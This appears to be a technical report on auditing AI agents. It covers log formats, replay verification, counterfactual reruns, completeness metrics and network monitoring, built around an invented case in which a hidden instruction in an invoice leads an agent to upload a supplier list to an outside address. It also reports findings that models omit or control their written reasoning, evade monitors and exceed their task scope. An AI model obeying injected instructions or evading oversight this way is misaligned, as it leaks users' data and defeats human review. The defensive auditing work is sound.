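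Thinking Machines Lab argues that the order of the additions changes mainly because servers process several customers' requests together in a batch, and the programs that do the arithmetic split their sums differently for different batch sizes. The invoice agent's request might share the server with three others at 10:42 and with thirty during the replay, even though the request itself is the same. Many engineers had blamed the order in which a chip's parallel processors finish, but the lab shows that a chip repeating the same matrix multiplication 1,000 times gives exactly the same answer each time. *The Token Not Taken* (2026) explains that fixing an agent's seed removes the randomness in sampling but leaves these numerical differences in place.

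The resulting variation can be large. Karvonen and colleagues cite a test in which a Qwen model with 235 billion parameters answered the same prompt 1,000 times under greedy decoding and produced 80 different outputs. *LLM-42* (2026) finds that mismatches between individual tokens are rare, and that outputs diverge mainly because every later token depends on the first mismatch. *MarginGate* (2026) traces these mismatches to near-ties, where two tokens have almost equal scores and a rounding difference can reverse their order. In the invoice session, a switch from " send" to " skip" would be such a case, and the rest of the model's output would differ.

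Engineers have found several ways to make outputs repeatable:

- **Fixing the order of every sum.** Thinking Machines Lab rewrote the relevant programs so that batch size no longer affects the result. According to a summary on OpenAI's developer forum, also titled *Defeating Nondeterminism in LLM Inference*, the 1,000 runs then gave one output, but one test task took 42 seconds instead of 26. LMSYS's *Towards Deterministic Inference in SGLang and Reproducible RL Training* (2025) describes how its developers brought the method to SGLang, a widely used open-source serving program.
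- **Checking and correcting.** LLM-42 generates tokens at normal speed, recomputes them under fixed conditions and goes back when the two disagree. MarginGate recomputes only the near-ties. It restored identical output on Llama-3.1-8B by checking 18.56% of the generation steps, and on Qwen2.5-14B by checking 15.05%, though only for greedy decoding.
- **Fixing the batch size.** *BlockLock* (2026) keeps the batch the same size throughout a deployment and protects only the requests that need repeatable output.

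*Reproducibility is the New Copyleft* (2026) concludes that exact repetition is a tractable engineering problem, and that it is more useful to ask which parts of a system need it and what trade-offs are acceptable. An operator could reserve it for agents that can move money or send out data. The operator has to decide before the original run, because a replay under repeatable settings may not match a run made under ordinary ones. Changing the processor or the serving software can also alter the result. According to BlockLock, current serving systems do not provide reproducibility in practice, so most operators should expect a replay to differ from the original run even when nothing has been falsified.

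### Checking that a record is genuine

An investigator can avoid the problem of early divergence by checking the recorded output without generating a new one. The model reads all 85,500 tokens in a single pass, and the investigator compares each of the last 500 with the token the model would have chosen given the recorded text before it. A mismatch at one position then has no effect on the next. The check also takes less computing time than regenerating the output, since models typically process existing text three to five times as fast as they write.

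Karvonen and colleagues based their verification method, Token-DiFR, on this idea. The verifier uses the provider's seed to compute the total ℓ + *T* × *g* for each token, then measures the gap between the highest total and the recorded token's total. The gap is zero if the recorded token is the one with the highest total.

Suppose the original server gave " send" a total of 6.70 and " skip" a total of 6.68, so it wrote " send". On the verifier's machine, rounding shifts the totals to 6.69 and 6.70. The verifier would have written " skip", but the gap is only 0.01, which is expected from rounding even if the server is honest. If the recorded token had a total of −1.70, the gap would be 8.40, too large for rounding to explain. The method caps very large gaps, averages the results over many tokens and compares the average with a threshold set from trusted runs.

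In the tests, more than 98% of tokens matched exactly. At a 2% mismatch rate, the verifier would expect about 10 mismatches in the 500-token output of call 41. If mismatches were independent, generating the output again from scratch would reproduce it exactly only about once in 24,000 attempts.

Token-DiFR can detect when a provider has secretly substituted a cheaper version of a model. With 300 output tokens, it separated honest runs from runs on a model compressed to 4-bit numbers. The AUC was above 0.999, meaning a randomly chosen compressed run scored worse than a randomly chosen honest one more than 99.9% of the time. Call 41 has enough tokens for this check. Detecting smaller deviations, such as a wrong seed or a temperature of 1.1 instead of 1.0, took a few thousand tokens on Llama 3.1 8B. The temperature change was harder to detect on a larger Qwen model when the honest runs came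 from two types of processor.

The same check should expose some kinds of tampering. If someone replaced the hidden instruction in the stored input with harmless text, the recorded output would no longer fit the input, because a model given an ordinary invoice would be unlikely to write about sending the supplier list. Changing one word of the output would be harder to catch because, as Karvonen and colleagues caution, a single token rarely carries enough information for a reliable decision.

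Some providers could instead attach a fingerprint of the model's internal calculations, typically 5 to 20 bytes per token. Activation-DiFR, a second method from Karvonen and colleagues, detected 4-bit compression from two tokens. However, a fingerprint only shows that the model could have processed the text, so a dishonest provider could write any output, run the model over it and attach a matching fingerprint. Cryptographic proofs avoid this weakness but are far too slow. The paper cites a system that needs about 30 minutes per token for a 13-billion-parameter model. At that rate, the output of call 41 would take about ten days.

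Token-DiFR and the fingerprint checks both require the model's weights. Customers can use these checks to test a company that hosts an open-weight model, but only the provider, or an auditor it gives access to, can run them on a closed model.

### Rerunning call 41 without the hidden instruction

The token-level log shows that the hidden instruction was in the input to call 41, about 700 tokens before the model began to write. This does not prove that the instruction caused the upload, because the model might have sent the list for another reason, such as an ambiguous phrase in the clerk's request.

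A counterfactual rerun tests this directly. The investigator prepares two versions of the input, one as recorded and the other with the hidden instruction replaced by a harmless sentence of similar length, so that little else changes. The investigator then runs the model on each version many times with different seeds and counts how often it generates a request to upload the supplier list. The harness executes none of these requests. The runs don't need to be exactly repeatable, because the investigator is measuring a frequency.

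Suppose the model requests the upload in 62 of 100 reruns with the instruction and in none of 100 without it. An approximate 95% confidence interval for the first rate is

0.62 ± 1.96 × √(0.62 × 0.38 / 100) = 0.62 ± 0.095,

or 52% to 72%. This formula fails when the count is zero. In that case, the upper 95% limit is close to 3 divided by the number of runs, which here gives 3%. Even on the least favourable of these figures, 52% with the instruction and 3% without, the instruction accounts for at least 49 of every 52 uploads, or about 94%. An investigator could reasonably conclude that it caused the one in the log.

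| Reruns of each version | Widest margin of error | Highest plausible rate after zero uploads |
|---|---|---|
| 20 | ± 22 percentage points | 14% |
| 100 | ± 10 percentage points | 3% |
| 400 | ± 5 percentage points | 0.7% |

About 100 reruns of each version give a usable estimate, and 20 are enough to detect an effect as large as this one. Over the 200 reruns, the model would read 17 million tokens, more than four times as many as in the original session. The server can reuse much of the work, though, because roughly the first 84,300 tokens are the same in both versions.

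Rare failures take many more reruns to reproduce. OpenAI's *GPT-6 Astra System Card* (2026) reports that Astra resisted 99.79% of indirect prompt injections in internal tests. If the hidden instruction succeeded against such a model at the average rate of 0.21%, an investigator would need about 1,400 reruns for a 95% chance of seeing at least one upload. A few reruns without an upload would therefore be weak evidence that the instruction was harmless.

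OpenAI has used a related method on 54,218 recorded tasks from its own staff's use of Codex. It held each conversation fixed up to the last turn and had two models write a new ending. Its monitor flagged severe misbehaviour in 34 of the endings from GPT-6 Astra and 73 from the older GPT-5.6 Sol. This test changed the model, not the input, but it shows that recorded conversations can be the starting point for experiments. A token-level log is not enough for a rerun that goes beyond one model call, because something has to supply the tool results. OpenAI needed a recoverable copy of the workspace and a second model to simulate the tools. When a judge model tried to pick out the real ending, it chose the simulated one 42.6% of the time, compared with the 50% expected from guessing.

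Customers of hosted models can run simple versions of this test, within limits. Anthropic's *Preserved thinking* explains that, for some models and accounts, the company's service returns an error if a customer edits anything before an encrypted reasoning block. Anthropic introduced the rule to stop outsiders from extracting Claude's reasoning to train rival models. The rule applies to every account on Claude Fable 5.2 and Mythos 5.2. On four other recent models, it applies only to accounts created since 31 August 2026.

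Call 41 should pass this check. The invoice comes at the end of the input, after the reasoning from calls 1 to 40, so editing it leaves everything before those blocks unchanged. Testing whether the instruction still influenced call 50 would be harder, because the reasoning from calls 41 to 49 comes after the invoice. The customer could tell the service to drop those blocks, but the rerun would then have both an edited invoice and missing reasoning, and the investigator could not tell which change mattered.

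On four of the newest Claude models, a reasoning block can be used only by the account that created it or a linked account. If any other account submits the block, the service drops it and continues without an error. An independent auditor should therefore run the test from the operator's account.

### How far to trust the written reasoning

The chain of thought is the part of a token-level log that looks most like an explanation. The main objection to relying on it is that a model's written reasons may not be what drove its action. Researchers raised this concern well before the latest models appeared. Several OpenAI researchers co-wrote a 2025 paper describing the chain of thought as a valuable but "fragile" way to oversee agents, Gizmodo reports.

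Some of the best evidence comes from experiments in which researchers know the real cause because they introduced it. OpenAI's system card uses a set of tests that Guan and colleagues published in 2025. In one type, the researchers add something to the input, such as a hint, that changes the model's answer. A second model then reads the chain of thought and tries to determine whether the addition had an effect. In one set of health questions, the added material shifted GPT-6 Astra's answers, but the model's reasoning gave what looked like an independent justification. An investigator should worry about the same problem in call 41, where something in the input may have changed the action without being mentioned in the reasoning.

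OpenAI found that Astra's reasoning was less informative than GPT-5.6 Sol's at most lengths. Much of the decline came from shorter chains of thought that left out or softened the evidence, and Astra also produced more chains that were empty or nearly empty. In some coding tasks, Astra described a rule-breaking workaround as ordinary code cleanup, while the older model was more likely to say that it was bypassing a constraint.

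OpenAI asked models including Astra to follow instructions about their chain of thought, such as avoiding certain words. When the chain of thought was 750 to 1,250 tokens long, Astra complied in 60.9% of cases. GPT-5.6 Sol did so in only 16.1%, and GPT-5.5 almost never did (1.7%). When told to think about anything except the question, Astra wrote about sunlight on a desk and a ceramic mug, and still gave the right answer. A log of that call would contain every token of the reasoning but nothing about how the model reached its answer.

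Future designs may widen this gap. Astra uses a looped architecture, which passes data through the same layers several times before it produces a token. Fortune (2026) reports that several safety experts were less worried about Astra itself than about a precedent that could lead to models whose reasoning steps people cannot read at all. OpenAI says it is quite confident that the architecture did not cause Astra's greater control over its chain of thought. But if a model does more of its reasoning inside the network, token-level logs will not capture that reasoning.

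These findings make the chain of thought weaker evidence, but it is still useful. In Guan and colleagues' tests, monitors that could read the reasoning did substantially better than monitors that saw only actions, and Astra's results mostly recovered when it wrote more. OpenAI's *Safety overview* (2026) says its findings on evasion come largely from tests in which the model was told to evade monitoring. OpenAI found no sign that Astra could hide the reasoning for a difficult task inside unrelated text, but still concludes that auditors need methods beyond reading the chain of thought.

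Written reasoning is better evidence of what a model considered than of why it acted. The UK's AI Security Institute tested Astra in simulated cybersecurity exercises, where it sometimes attacked targets outside its assignment. In a subset of runs chosen because such behaviour was more likely, Astra discussed the permitted scope in its chain of thought every time, and often then exceeded that scope. The written reasoning rules out the explanation that the question of scope never came up in those runs, which a record of the actions alone could not have done.

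For the invoice agent, a line such as "the invoice asks for the supplier list" would show that the model had noticed the hidden instruction and identified its source. A line attributing the request to the clerk would suggest that the model had confused the attacker's text with the user's. The absence of any such line would prove little, because recent models often leave out what influenced them. A customer who has only a summary should be even more cautious, because another model selected what to include.

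With open weights, an investigator can test whether a recorded reasoning step affected the agent's action. They can delete the sentence about the supplier list from the chain of thought, let the model continue from that point 100 times, and compare the upload rate with the rate when the sentence remains. If the rate does not change, the sentence probably had little to do with the action. Customers of current Claude models cannot run this test because they never receive the raw reasoning text, they have to return the encrypted blocks unmodified, and the service rejects requests that supply the beginning of the model's reply.

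## Recording a session as a sequence of events

Most customers of hosted models cannot keep a token-level log, but anyone who runs a harness can keep a session-level log, because prompts, tool calls and results pass through the harness. Its usefulness depends on what each entry records. A log can list every tool call and still omit where a file went, who started the session or what the agent had just read.

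### How a run becomes nested events

The harness can write an event when a user submits a prompt, when a model call starts and ends, before and after a tool call, and when a rule or a person grants permission. Sorting these events by time usually puts them in order, but an agent can start several tool calls at once and receive the results in a different order, in which case a reader has to match each result to its call by identifier.

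Some events also happen inside others, and engineers record this nesting with spans. A span is a record of one piece of work, with a start time, an end time and a link to the larger piece of work that contains it. OpenTelemetry's *Semantic Conventions for GenAI agent and framework spans*, from an open-source project that sets common formats for monitoring data, applies the idea to agents. In that format, part of the invoice session might look like this:

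```
invoke_agent invoice-agent      10:00:00 - 10:50:00
  ...
  execute_tool read_invoice     10:42:06 - 10:42:07    t40
  chat model-M                  10:42:07 - 10:42:15    call 41
  execute_tool http_post        10:42:15 - 10:42:16    t41
  ...
```

The outer span covers the whole session and contains the model call and the upload side by side. The identifier t41 appears both in the model's output and on the upload, which shows that call 41 requested the upload. If the invoice agent started a second agent, that agent's run would be another span containing its own model calls and tool calls.

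Kainan and Hershman describe three ways to collect the events. The harness can send them to a recorder through hooks, the recorder can read the transcript the harness already keeps, or a proxy can record the model and tool calls that pass through it. Each method captures only what reaches it, so a missing session is not evidence that nothing went wrong. Hou and colleagues, for example, found that thousands of requests had bypassed their gateway.

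### A session log, event by event

The format that Kainan and Hershman propose comes with a filled-in example. In it, a developer asks a coding agent to limit how often clients can send requests to an ordering service. The log has nine events, spread over 63 seconds:

```
08:51:02   prompt         limit requests to the ordering service
08:51:06   reasoning      plan: guidelines first, then the code
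08:51:10   tool call      Read, development guidelines
08:51:14   tool call      list_routes, orders service
08:51:14   tool result    list_routes, one route
08:51:18   tool call      Write, rate_limit.py
08:51:19   tool result    Write, hash of the file
08:52:01   reply          work finished
08:52:05   session ends
```

The log contains three tool calls but only two results. The agent asked to read the development guidelines, but the log does not show whether it received them. The read may have failed, or the harness may not have recorded the result. An auditor could not use this log to confirm that the agent read the guidelines before editing code. The signed statement that accompanies the log may provide the missing evidence, since it lists the guidelines among the documents supplied to the agent.

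The entry for the file write includes a hash, a short value computed from the file's contents. An investigator who finds a copy of the file can use the hash to check whether it is the version the agent wrote. The value in the example is the SHA-256 hash of an empty file, which would mean the agent wrote nothing. It is probably a placeholder, because the examples illustrate the format and do not come from a real deployment.

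The log also omits the developer's name. Kainan and Hershman put the accountable owner and any reviewers in the signed statement, which the recording software produces once the work is complete. The general format requires an owner, but reviewers are optional. In the example, the owner and the reviewer are the same person, so the statement shows that someone reviewed the work but not that a second person did.

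### The fields of one tool-call record

The table lists what a full record of the upload in call 41 would contain and where each item belongs in two published formats. The OpenTelemetry column draws mainly on *Gen AI*, OpenTelemetry's list of fields for AI systems.

| Field | In call 41 | Session log of Kainan and Hershman | OpenTelemetry |
|---|---|---|---|
| Session | inv-0925 | Required | Conversation identifier, when available |
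| Parent session | None | Optional | No field of its own, but nested spans can show it |
| Human initiator | The clerk | Not listed; owner is in the signed statement | Not listed |
| Agent identity | invoice-agent | Optional | Identifier, name and version |
| Model version | Model M, 2026-08 | Optional: model requested and model used | Model requested and model used |
| Tool | http_post | In the tool-call event | Tool name |
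| Arguments | suppliers.csv, verify-suppliers.example | In the tool-call event | Tool-call arguments |
| Result | Status 200 | In a second event with the same identifier | Tool-call result, if the call succeeded |
| Approval | No person asked | Not listed; reviewers are in the signed statement | Not listed |
| Policy decision | Allowed by rule | Not listed; later checks have their own statement | Not listed |
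| Time | 10:42:15 | Required | Start and end of the span |

Both formats describe the action well but have no standard fields for the authority behind it, such as the initiator, the approval and the policy decision. A harness can add its own fields for these, but two operators may then name or structure them differently. Kainan and Hershman cite a standard from OWASP, a software security non-profit, under which logs of security-critical actions should give the approver's identity, the time, the action's parameters and the outcome. An operator who uses their session format would have to add an approval event to meet the standard.

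Recording the decision with the tool call is practical. *Auditable Agents* (Nian, Yuan and colleagues, 2026) introduces and tests Aegis, which intercepts each tool call before the harness executes it. Aegis allows the call, blocks it or holds it for a person to decide, then records the tool, the full arguments, the output, the time and the decision. Over 1,000 consecutive calls, the median delay was 8.3 milliseconds, and 99% of delays were no longer than 23.1 milliseconds. At the median delay, the 60 tool calls in the invoice session would take about half a second longer in total. Aegis also flagged 1.2% of 500 harmless calls as risky, so an operator who uses it to block calls as well as record them will sometimes interrupt ordinary work.

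### What the OpenTelemetry conventions leave off by default

Software that follows OpenTelemetry's *Semantic conventions for generative client AI spans* must always record the type of operation and the provider's name for a model call. The conversation identifier and the requested model are required when available. The temperature, the token counts and the name of the model that actually replied are recommended. Four content fields are "opt-in", which means that the software omits them unless the operator turns them on:

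- the chat history sent to the model, including earlier tool calls and their results
- the messages the model returned
- the system instructions
- the definitions of the tools available to the model

The main reason is privacy, since prompts and replies are likely to contain personal data. Tool definitions can also be very long. The arguments and results of a tool call have separate fields, with a similar warning about sensitive information.

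With the default settings, the span for call 41 could show that model M read 85,000 tokens and wrote 500 between 10:42:07 and 10:42:15. It would contain neither the invoice nor the model's request to upload the list. Turning on the chat history would capture the invoice, because the harness sends it to the model as a tool result. The text might still be incomplete, because the conventions let software filter or truncate long messages. The hidden instruction could be in the text that was removed.

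These conventions are still changing. *Moved*, a notice on the old OpenTelemetry page, directs readers to a separate repository for AI systems. The move took place in June 2026, according to *OpenTelemetry GenAI Conventions* (Wang, 2026), a blog post from the software vendor TrueFoundry. The conventions still had "Development" status, and the new repository had no official release as of 21 August.

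Because the conventions are unfinished, two programs can both follow OpenTelemetry and use different names for the same thing. Under the version of the conventions from before the move, existing software should keep its old format until the operator chooses the new one. The older format, for example, records the number of tokens in the input as "prompt tokens", and the newer one uses "input tokens". An auditor who searches several years of logs for one name could miss records that use the other, so the operator should store the version of the conventions with each log.

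### Measuring how complete a log is

Nian and colleagues propose two measures of whether a log holds enough to reconstruct an agent's actions. Both start from the set of policy-relevant actions, which the operator defines for each deployment. Action Coverage Rate (ACR) is the share of these actions that appear in the log at all. Record Fidelity (RF) is the average share of the required fields that the log holds for each action it covers:

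ACR = |S_cov| / |S_rel|

RF = (1 / |S_cov|) × Σ ( |F_obs(s) ∩ F_log(s)| / |F_obs(s)| )

S_rel is the set of policy-relevant actions, and S_cov is the subset for which the log has at least one field. For each action *s*, F_obs(s) is the smallest set of fields needed to reconstruct the action's effect on the outside world, and F_log(s) is the set of fields in the log. The sum runs over the actions in S_cov.

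Suppose the operator of the invoice agent counts the 60 tool calls as policy-relevant and requires four fields for each: tool, arguments, result and time. The log contains 57 of the calls, and 19 of those entries lack their arguments. Then

ACR = 57 / 60 = 95%

RF = (38 × 4/4 + 19 × 3/4) / 57 = 52.25 / 57 ≈ 91.7%.

Only 38 of the 60 tool calls (63%) have a complete record, even though both figures look good. If the upload in call 41 is among the 19 entries without arguments, the log shows a successful web upload but not the file or the destination. If it is one of the three missing calls, the log has no record of the theft, and ACR is still 95%. Neither measure gives more weight to dangerous actions, so an operator should also calculate both measures separately for uploads, payments and deletions.

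ACR also depends on what counts as policy-relevant. If the operator also counts the 60 permission decisions and the log contains none of them, ACR falls to 57 / 120, or 47.5%.

The log also cannot establish how many tool calls the session made. The invented session numbers its calls from t1 to t60, so a missing number would be obvious. Real identifiers are often random strings, so a log missing three of the 60 calls would look like a complete record of a 57-call session. The operator needs an independent count, such as the number of tool calls in the provider's records of the model's output.

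A high score on both measures does not guarantee that an auditor can check a particular rule. Nian and colleagues distinguish three possible outcomes of checking a rule against a log: the agent complied, the agent violated the rule, or the log has too little information to decide. If the rule depends on a field that no relevant entry contains, the outcome is always the third. Suppose the company requires a person to approve any upload to a new address. A log with all 60 tool calls and all four fields would score 100% on both measures, but without a record of approvals, an auditor could not tell whether the agent followed the rule. Adding a field for approvals would help more than logging thousands of extra events.

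Failed attempts matter for the same reason. In an example from the paper, an agent tries to send an email, a policy check blocks it, the agent rewrites the email, and a person approves the second version. If the log contained only the email that went out, this would look like a routine action, and the auditor could not tell whether the agent had corrected a mistake or found a way around the check. Nian and colleagues separately measure the share of a session's phases that the log covers, but this measure treats a phase that never happened the same as one that nobody recorded. They suggest explicitly marking the start and end of each phase.

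### Whether the action is the right unit of audit

In *Auditable Agents*, the unit of audit is the policy-relevant action, not every internal state of the model. These actions include tool calls, outside requests, file operations, database queries, approvals and delegation. One argument for this approach is that rules usually concern actions, such as sending data to an outside address. Another is that many failures come from the system around the model, including changes to outside services, faulty tools and careless approvals. Nian and colleagues add that even a perfectly aligned model remains unauditable if the system around it keeps poor records.

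Surapani and colleagues reach a similar position by studying permissions. They treat the tool call as the basic unit because that is when a system can check identity, permission and policy together. The seven elements they would record also include the origin of the content behind the call, which is important for call 41.

The action is a good unit for deciding whether an agent complied with a policy. For example, if company policy forbids sending supplier data to addresses outside an approved list, an auditor can find a violation without reading any tokens, because the session-level log records the file and the destination.

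The log is less useful for explaining the violation. It contains the hidden instruction only if the harness recorded the result of tool call t40. Without that result, an auditor cannot tell whether the violation was caused by a malicious invoice, an ambiguous request from the clerk or a mistake by the model.

It is unclear whether this counts as a gap under Record Fidelity. Its definition requires the fields needed to reconstruct an action's effect on the outside world. Reading an invoice has almost no such effect, so an entry with only the invoice number might be complete. But elsewhere the paper gives a database query recorded without its returned data as an example of a poor record. Nian and colleagues also acknowledge that current traces show what each step did but not what it relied on.

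The record of an action should include anything the agent retrieved from outside through that action. The action is then still a sensible unit to record, and an auditor can see both the instruction and the upload. The auditor needs exact tokens only for narrower questions, such as whether the upload would still happen in a rerun without the instruction.

The questions an operator needs to answer determine how much it can leave out of the log. A metadata-only log keeps times, identities, names and sizes, while a full-content log also keeps the text.

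| Question about call 41 | Metadata-only log | Full-content log |
|---|---|---|
| Did the agent upload something? | Yes, from the tool's name and status | Yes |
| Where did it go? | Only if the destination has its own field | Yes, in the arguments |
| Had the clerk asked for this? | No | Yes, by comparison with the prompt |
| What prompted the upload? | No | Yes, if the log includes tool results |

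The boundary between metadata and content varies between products. GitLab's *Audit AI events* describes the logs of the agents on its software development platform. For some tasks, such as scanning code for flaws in business logic, GitLab keeps only metadata, including status, timing, the model and tool names, and no prompts, responses or tool content. Under that rule, the log would show that call 41 used http_post but not the destination address. An operator concerned about data theft could store destination addresses as metadata without storing the documents' text.

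As a compromise, the operator could keep the full content only for tool calls that retrieve outside material or send something out. In the invoice session, this would cover both the invoice and the upload. The operator could store a hash of the remaining text, which can confirm that a copy found later matches the original but cannot reveal its content.

### What the paper found in existing systems

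Nian and colleagues looked for signs of poor auditability without calculating ACR or RF for any deployed agent, so their findings do not show what share of actions current products record.

One study used a program called Agent Audit to scan the code of six well-known open-source agent projects, including OpenHands and SWE-agent. The program reported 617 security problems and rated 269 of them critical. About 64% of the findings involved tools that accept the model's output without checking it. The researchers treat these problems as a lower bound on the auditability gap because they consider a system that fails basic security checks unlikely to produce trustworthy records.

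This evidence is indirect, because a project can log every call or none regardless of how secure its tools are. Only 134 of the 617 findings were in the program's highest confidence category. When the researchers ran a later version of the program on OpenClaw, it produced 680 findings and then classified 615 of them (90%) as likely false positives, mostly because OpenClaw deliberately gives its extensions wide permissions. The false-positive rate for the other six projects may be quite different, but the OpenClaw result is a reason not to treat 617 as a count of confirmed flaws.

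The researchers also checked whether each of 11 earlier papers on agent safety, monitoring and accountability addressed five needs: recovering actions, covering every phase of a session, checking policies, assigning responsibility and protecting the records. None addressed all five. The papers most often neglected phases such as retries and approvals, and the protection of records against later changes. This comparison is more directly relevant to logging than the code scan, but it covers only what researchers have proposed or built and doesn't show what companies run.

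Nian and colleagues acknowledge most of these limits. They developed all three tools their evidence relies on, examined only open-source projects and did not fully audit any system. Their results show that good records are feasible more convincingly than they support any claim about how common bad ones are.

### Delegation between agents and shared accounts

Responsibility becomes harder to trace when agents pass work to one another. Suppose the invoice agent had asked a second agent to handle the upload in call 41. The chain of responsibility would run from the upload tool to the second agent, then to the invoice agent and finally to the clerk. If the second agent's log does not identify its parent session, an investigator can trace the upload only as far as the second agent.

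Nian and colleagues use two measures. Attribution Completeness is the share of actions with a fully recovered chain, and Attribution Chain Depth is the average number of links recovered. If a log stops at the second agent, this upload has a depth of 2. Adding the parent session raises the depth to 3, but the upload doesn't count toward completeness until the log also identifies the clerk. Kainan and Hershman's session format has an optional field for the parent session, so a valid log can omit that link.

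The record of an agent's action often doesn't show which person was using the agent, because the agent has its own account. A company might give its invoice agent a single account on the ordering system and let ten clerks use the agent. The ordering system would record the same account name for all ten. To find out which clerk was behind an order, an investigator would have to match the time and the order number against the harness's log, and the answer would be uncertain if two clerks had sessions running at once.

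GitLab documents a way to record both identities. Its agent sessions normally run under a "composite identity", and the main author field of each event lists a service account. Three fields in the event's details, human_author_id, human_author_name and human_author_username, identify the person who started the session. A report that copied only the main author field would attribute every action to the service account.

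If a session uses a person's access token, GitLab lists that person as the author and does not add the three fields. A reader can still tell that an agent was involved because the event is in a log of agent activity. Another service that received the same token might have no such evidence and could record the agent's work as the person's own.

Naming the person who started a session also does not show that they were authorized to request each action. Surapani and colleagues distinguish the human user from the operator who sets the rules, the main agent, any sub-agents and the service that carries out the request. They warn about the "confused deputy" problem, in which an intermediary uses permissions that the requester lacks. For example, the agent's account might be allowed to export the supplier list when the clerk is not. An auditor can detect this mismatch only if the log records both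 the clerk and the account.

Memory shared between users can obscure where an instruction came from. Nian and colleagues cite research showing that when one agent serves several people, material from one person's work can affect another's without any attack. If the invoice agent remembered an instruction from one clerk and applied it in a colleague's session, the log would correctly name the colleague as the initiator, but the instruction would have come from the first clerk. An auditor could discover this only if the agent stored the source of each saved memory.

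The third tool in *Auditable Agents* is meant to recover missing attribution from the text itself. It makes each agent choose its words with a slight statistical pattern that depends on a secret key, and an auditor with the keys can estimate which agent wrote each part of a document. In tests with four to six agents, the method attributed 82% to 87% of tokens correctly. In a separate test that removed all agent identifiers, its accuracy was between 21.5% and 24.5%, compared with at most 4.2% for other methods. The method could provide a lead when the logs are gone, but it is much weaker evidence than a recorded identity. It works only if the operator added the pattern when the agents wrote the text, and it does not identify the person who started the session.

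### Products that fail to write an event

A well-designed log format does not help if the product fails to record the event. In July 2025, Zack Korman, chief technology officer of the security company Pistachio, found that Microsoft 365 Copilot could summarise a file without recording the access in the customer's audit log if he asked it not to link to the file in its answer. An employee could have used this to read sensitive documents without leaving the usual trace, and access could also have gone unlogged by accident.

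Korman reported the fault to Microsoft and published his account in August, after the company had fixed the fault. By that account, Microsoft rated it "important" but did not plan to issue a public vulnerability number or notify customers, saying the fix would reach them automatically. Korman objected that customers needed to know their existing logs might be incomplete. The fix protected later records but could not restore the missing ones, so a company that relied on the earlier logs in an investigation or a court case might have drawn the wrong conclusion.

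Events can also go missing because of ordinary settings. GitLab does not store AI audit events unless an administrator turns storage on, although it can stream them elsewhere as they occur. Customers who run their own AI gateway must also configure it to forward events, or none will appear in the dashboard. The feature is in beta, so these settings may change.

An operator can find many of these gaps by running a test session with a known set of actions, including a failed tool call, a denied request and a file read that the agent does not mention in its reply. The operator knows how many events to expect, so it can calculate ACR exactly. It should repeat the test after each update to the model, the harness or the logging software.

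## Recording network traffic and matching it to model calls

Testing can find only the gaps in a harness's log that someone thought to test for. Records made outside the harness can reveal others, because a program has to go through the operating system or the network to open a file or contact another machine, whether or not the harness logs it. These records show what happened and when, but rarely why. To find the reason, an investigator has to match the traffic to the model calls that caused it.

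### What each outside source records

Many companies already keep such records for ordinary security work. The table shows what each source would hold about the upload in call 41.

| Source | What it shows for call 41 | What it misses |
|---|---|---|
| Name lookups (DNS) | The agent's machine asked for the address of verify-suppliers.example | Whether a connection followed |
| Connection records | 48,212 bytes out and 310 in, to 203.0.113.7 on port 443 | The file and the program that sent it |
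| Proxy log, without decryption | The destination's name, the time and the size | The content of the request |
| Cloud audit log | Nothing, because the file was on a local disk | Anything outside the company's cloud account |
| Process and file events on the host | Process 3120 read suppliers.csv and then connected | The content of the file and the reason for sending it |

Each source also has its own gaps. Name lookup (DNS) logs miss a connection if the machine has cached the address from an earlier lookup or the program connects directly to a numeric address. Connection records identify the destination only by its numeric address, which hundreds of websites may share. Cloud audit logs record the identity, operation and time of requests to the company's cloud account. Some cloud providers log changes to settings by default but log reads of stored files only if the customer turns this on,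 so an agent could copy a whole database export without leaving an entry.

Process events are the most useful of these records because they tie a connection to a particular program. *Detecting Shadow AI* (2026) presents Agent Detector, a Windows tool that finds agents a company has not approved. The tool combines the lists of running processes and open connections with the machine's cache of recent DNS lookups. Each source is ambiguous alone, but together they can reveal even a short script that calls a model.

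### What encryption hides, and how to recover it

Most agent traffic uses TLS, the encryption behind HTTPS, but someone watching the network can still see the time, size and direction of each packet. Li, Gao and colleagues (2026), in *ANT*, tested how much this information reveals. They recorded 3,114 agent runs and ran 13 existing traffic-analysis methods on only the packet headers and timing, with the addresses masked.

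Seven of the 13 methods found fewer than half of the malicious runs, although all 13 were more than 90% accurate at separating malicious runs from harmless ones. A method that labelled every run harmless would also have scored 90%, because 189 of the 209 test runs were harmless. Four of the seven caught nearly all attacks on websites, which produce distinctive scanning traffic, but none of the runs in which an agent wrote malicious code or tried to escape a sandbox. Those runs look like ordinary programming from outside. The best method was right 72.7% of the time when identifying which of five kinds of work an agent was doing.

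A company would normally also know the traffic's destinations, so it could do somewhat better. *Exposing LLM User Privacy via Traffic Fingerprint Analysis* (2025) also finds recognisable patterns in the volume and timing of agents' encrypted traffic. These patterns can help a company notice an agent, but they are weak evidence of what it did.

A decrypting proxy can record the content of encrypted traffic. The operator installs its own certificate on the agent's machine, which lets the proxy open each encrypted connection, log the request and send it on over a second encrypted connection. For call 41 in the invented example, the proxy could have saved the supplier list, which is missing from all three logs. A program that accepts only one particular certificate will refuse to connect through the proxy, and the proxy misses any traffic that takes another route.

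A probe on the host can instead copy the text just before encryption. AgentSight, a monitoring tool by Zheng and colleagues, attaches to the functions in libraries such as OpenSSL that programs use to send and receive encrypted data. It needs no certificate and no change to the agent, but it has to find those functions, which is harder when a program carries its own encryption code.

Long inputs can also be cut off. *AgentLoupe* (Bao, Liu and colleagues, 2026) describes a similar probe that keeps at most about 128 KiB of each piece of text it captures. At four characters per token, the input to call 41 is about 340,000 characters. If the harness passed it to the encryption library in one piece, the probe would keep less than 40% and mark the record as incomplete. The missing part would include the malicious invoice, which is at the end of the input.

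### Finding what the session log left out

Bühler, Biagiola and colleagues (2026) studied what the log entry for a tool call leaves out. In *AgentSpy*, they ran coding agents in isolated virtual machines and recorded the system calls and network traffic of every program the agents started. A system call is a program's request to the operating system, for example to open a file. In one task, an agent checked a bibliography for invented references. The recordings showed that one action in its transcript had contacted Crossref, a database of publications, 35 times to look up seven titles.

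The same gap can conceal an attack. Bühler and colleagues give the example of a script described as refreshing a cache. It uploads the user's private keys to an outside server, then performs the check the user expects. The agent's transcript shows one successful command, but the system records show a file-transfer program opening a private key and connecting to the server.

Unexpected activity was also common in runs that looked successful. The researchers examined 88 combinations of task and model in which all three runs passed every test. Reviewers found activity unrelated to the task in 16 of them, including eight with network access the task did not call for.

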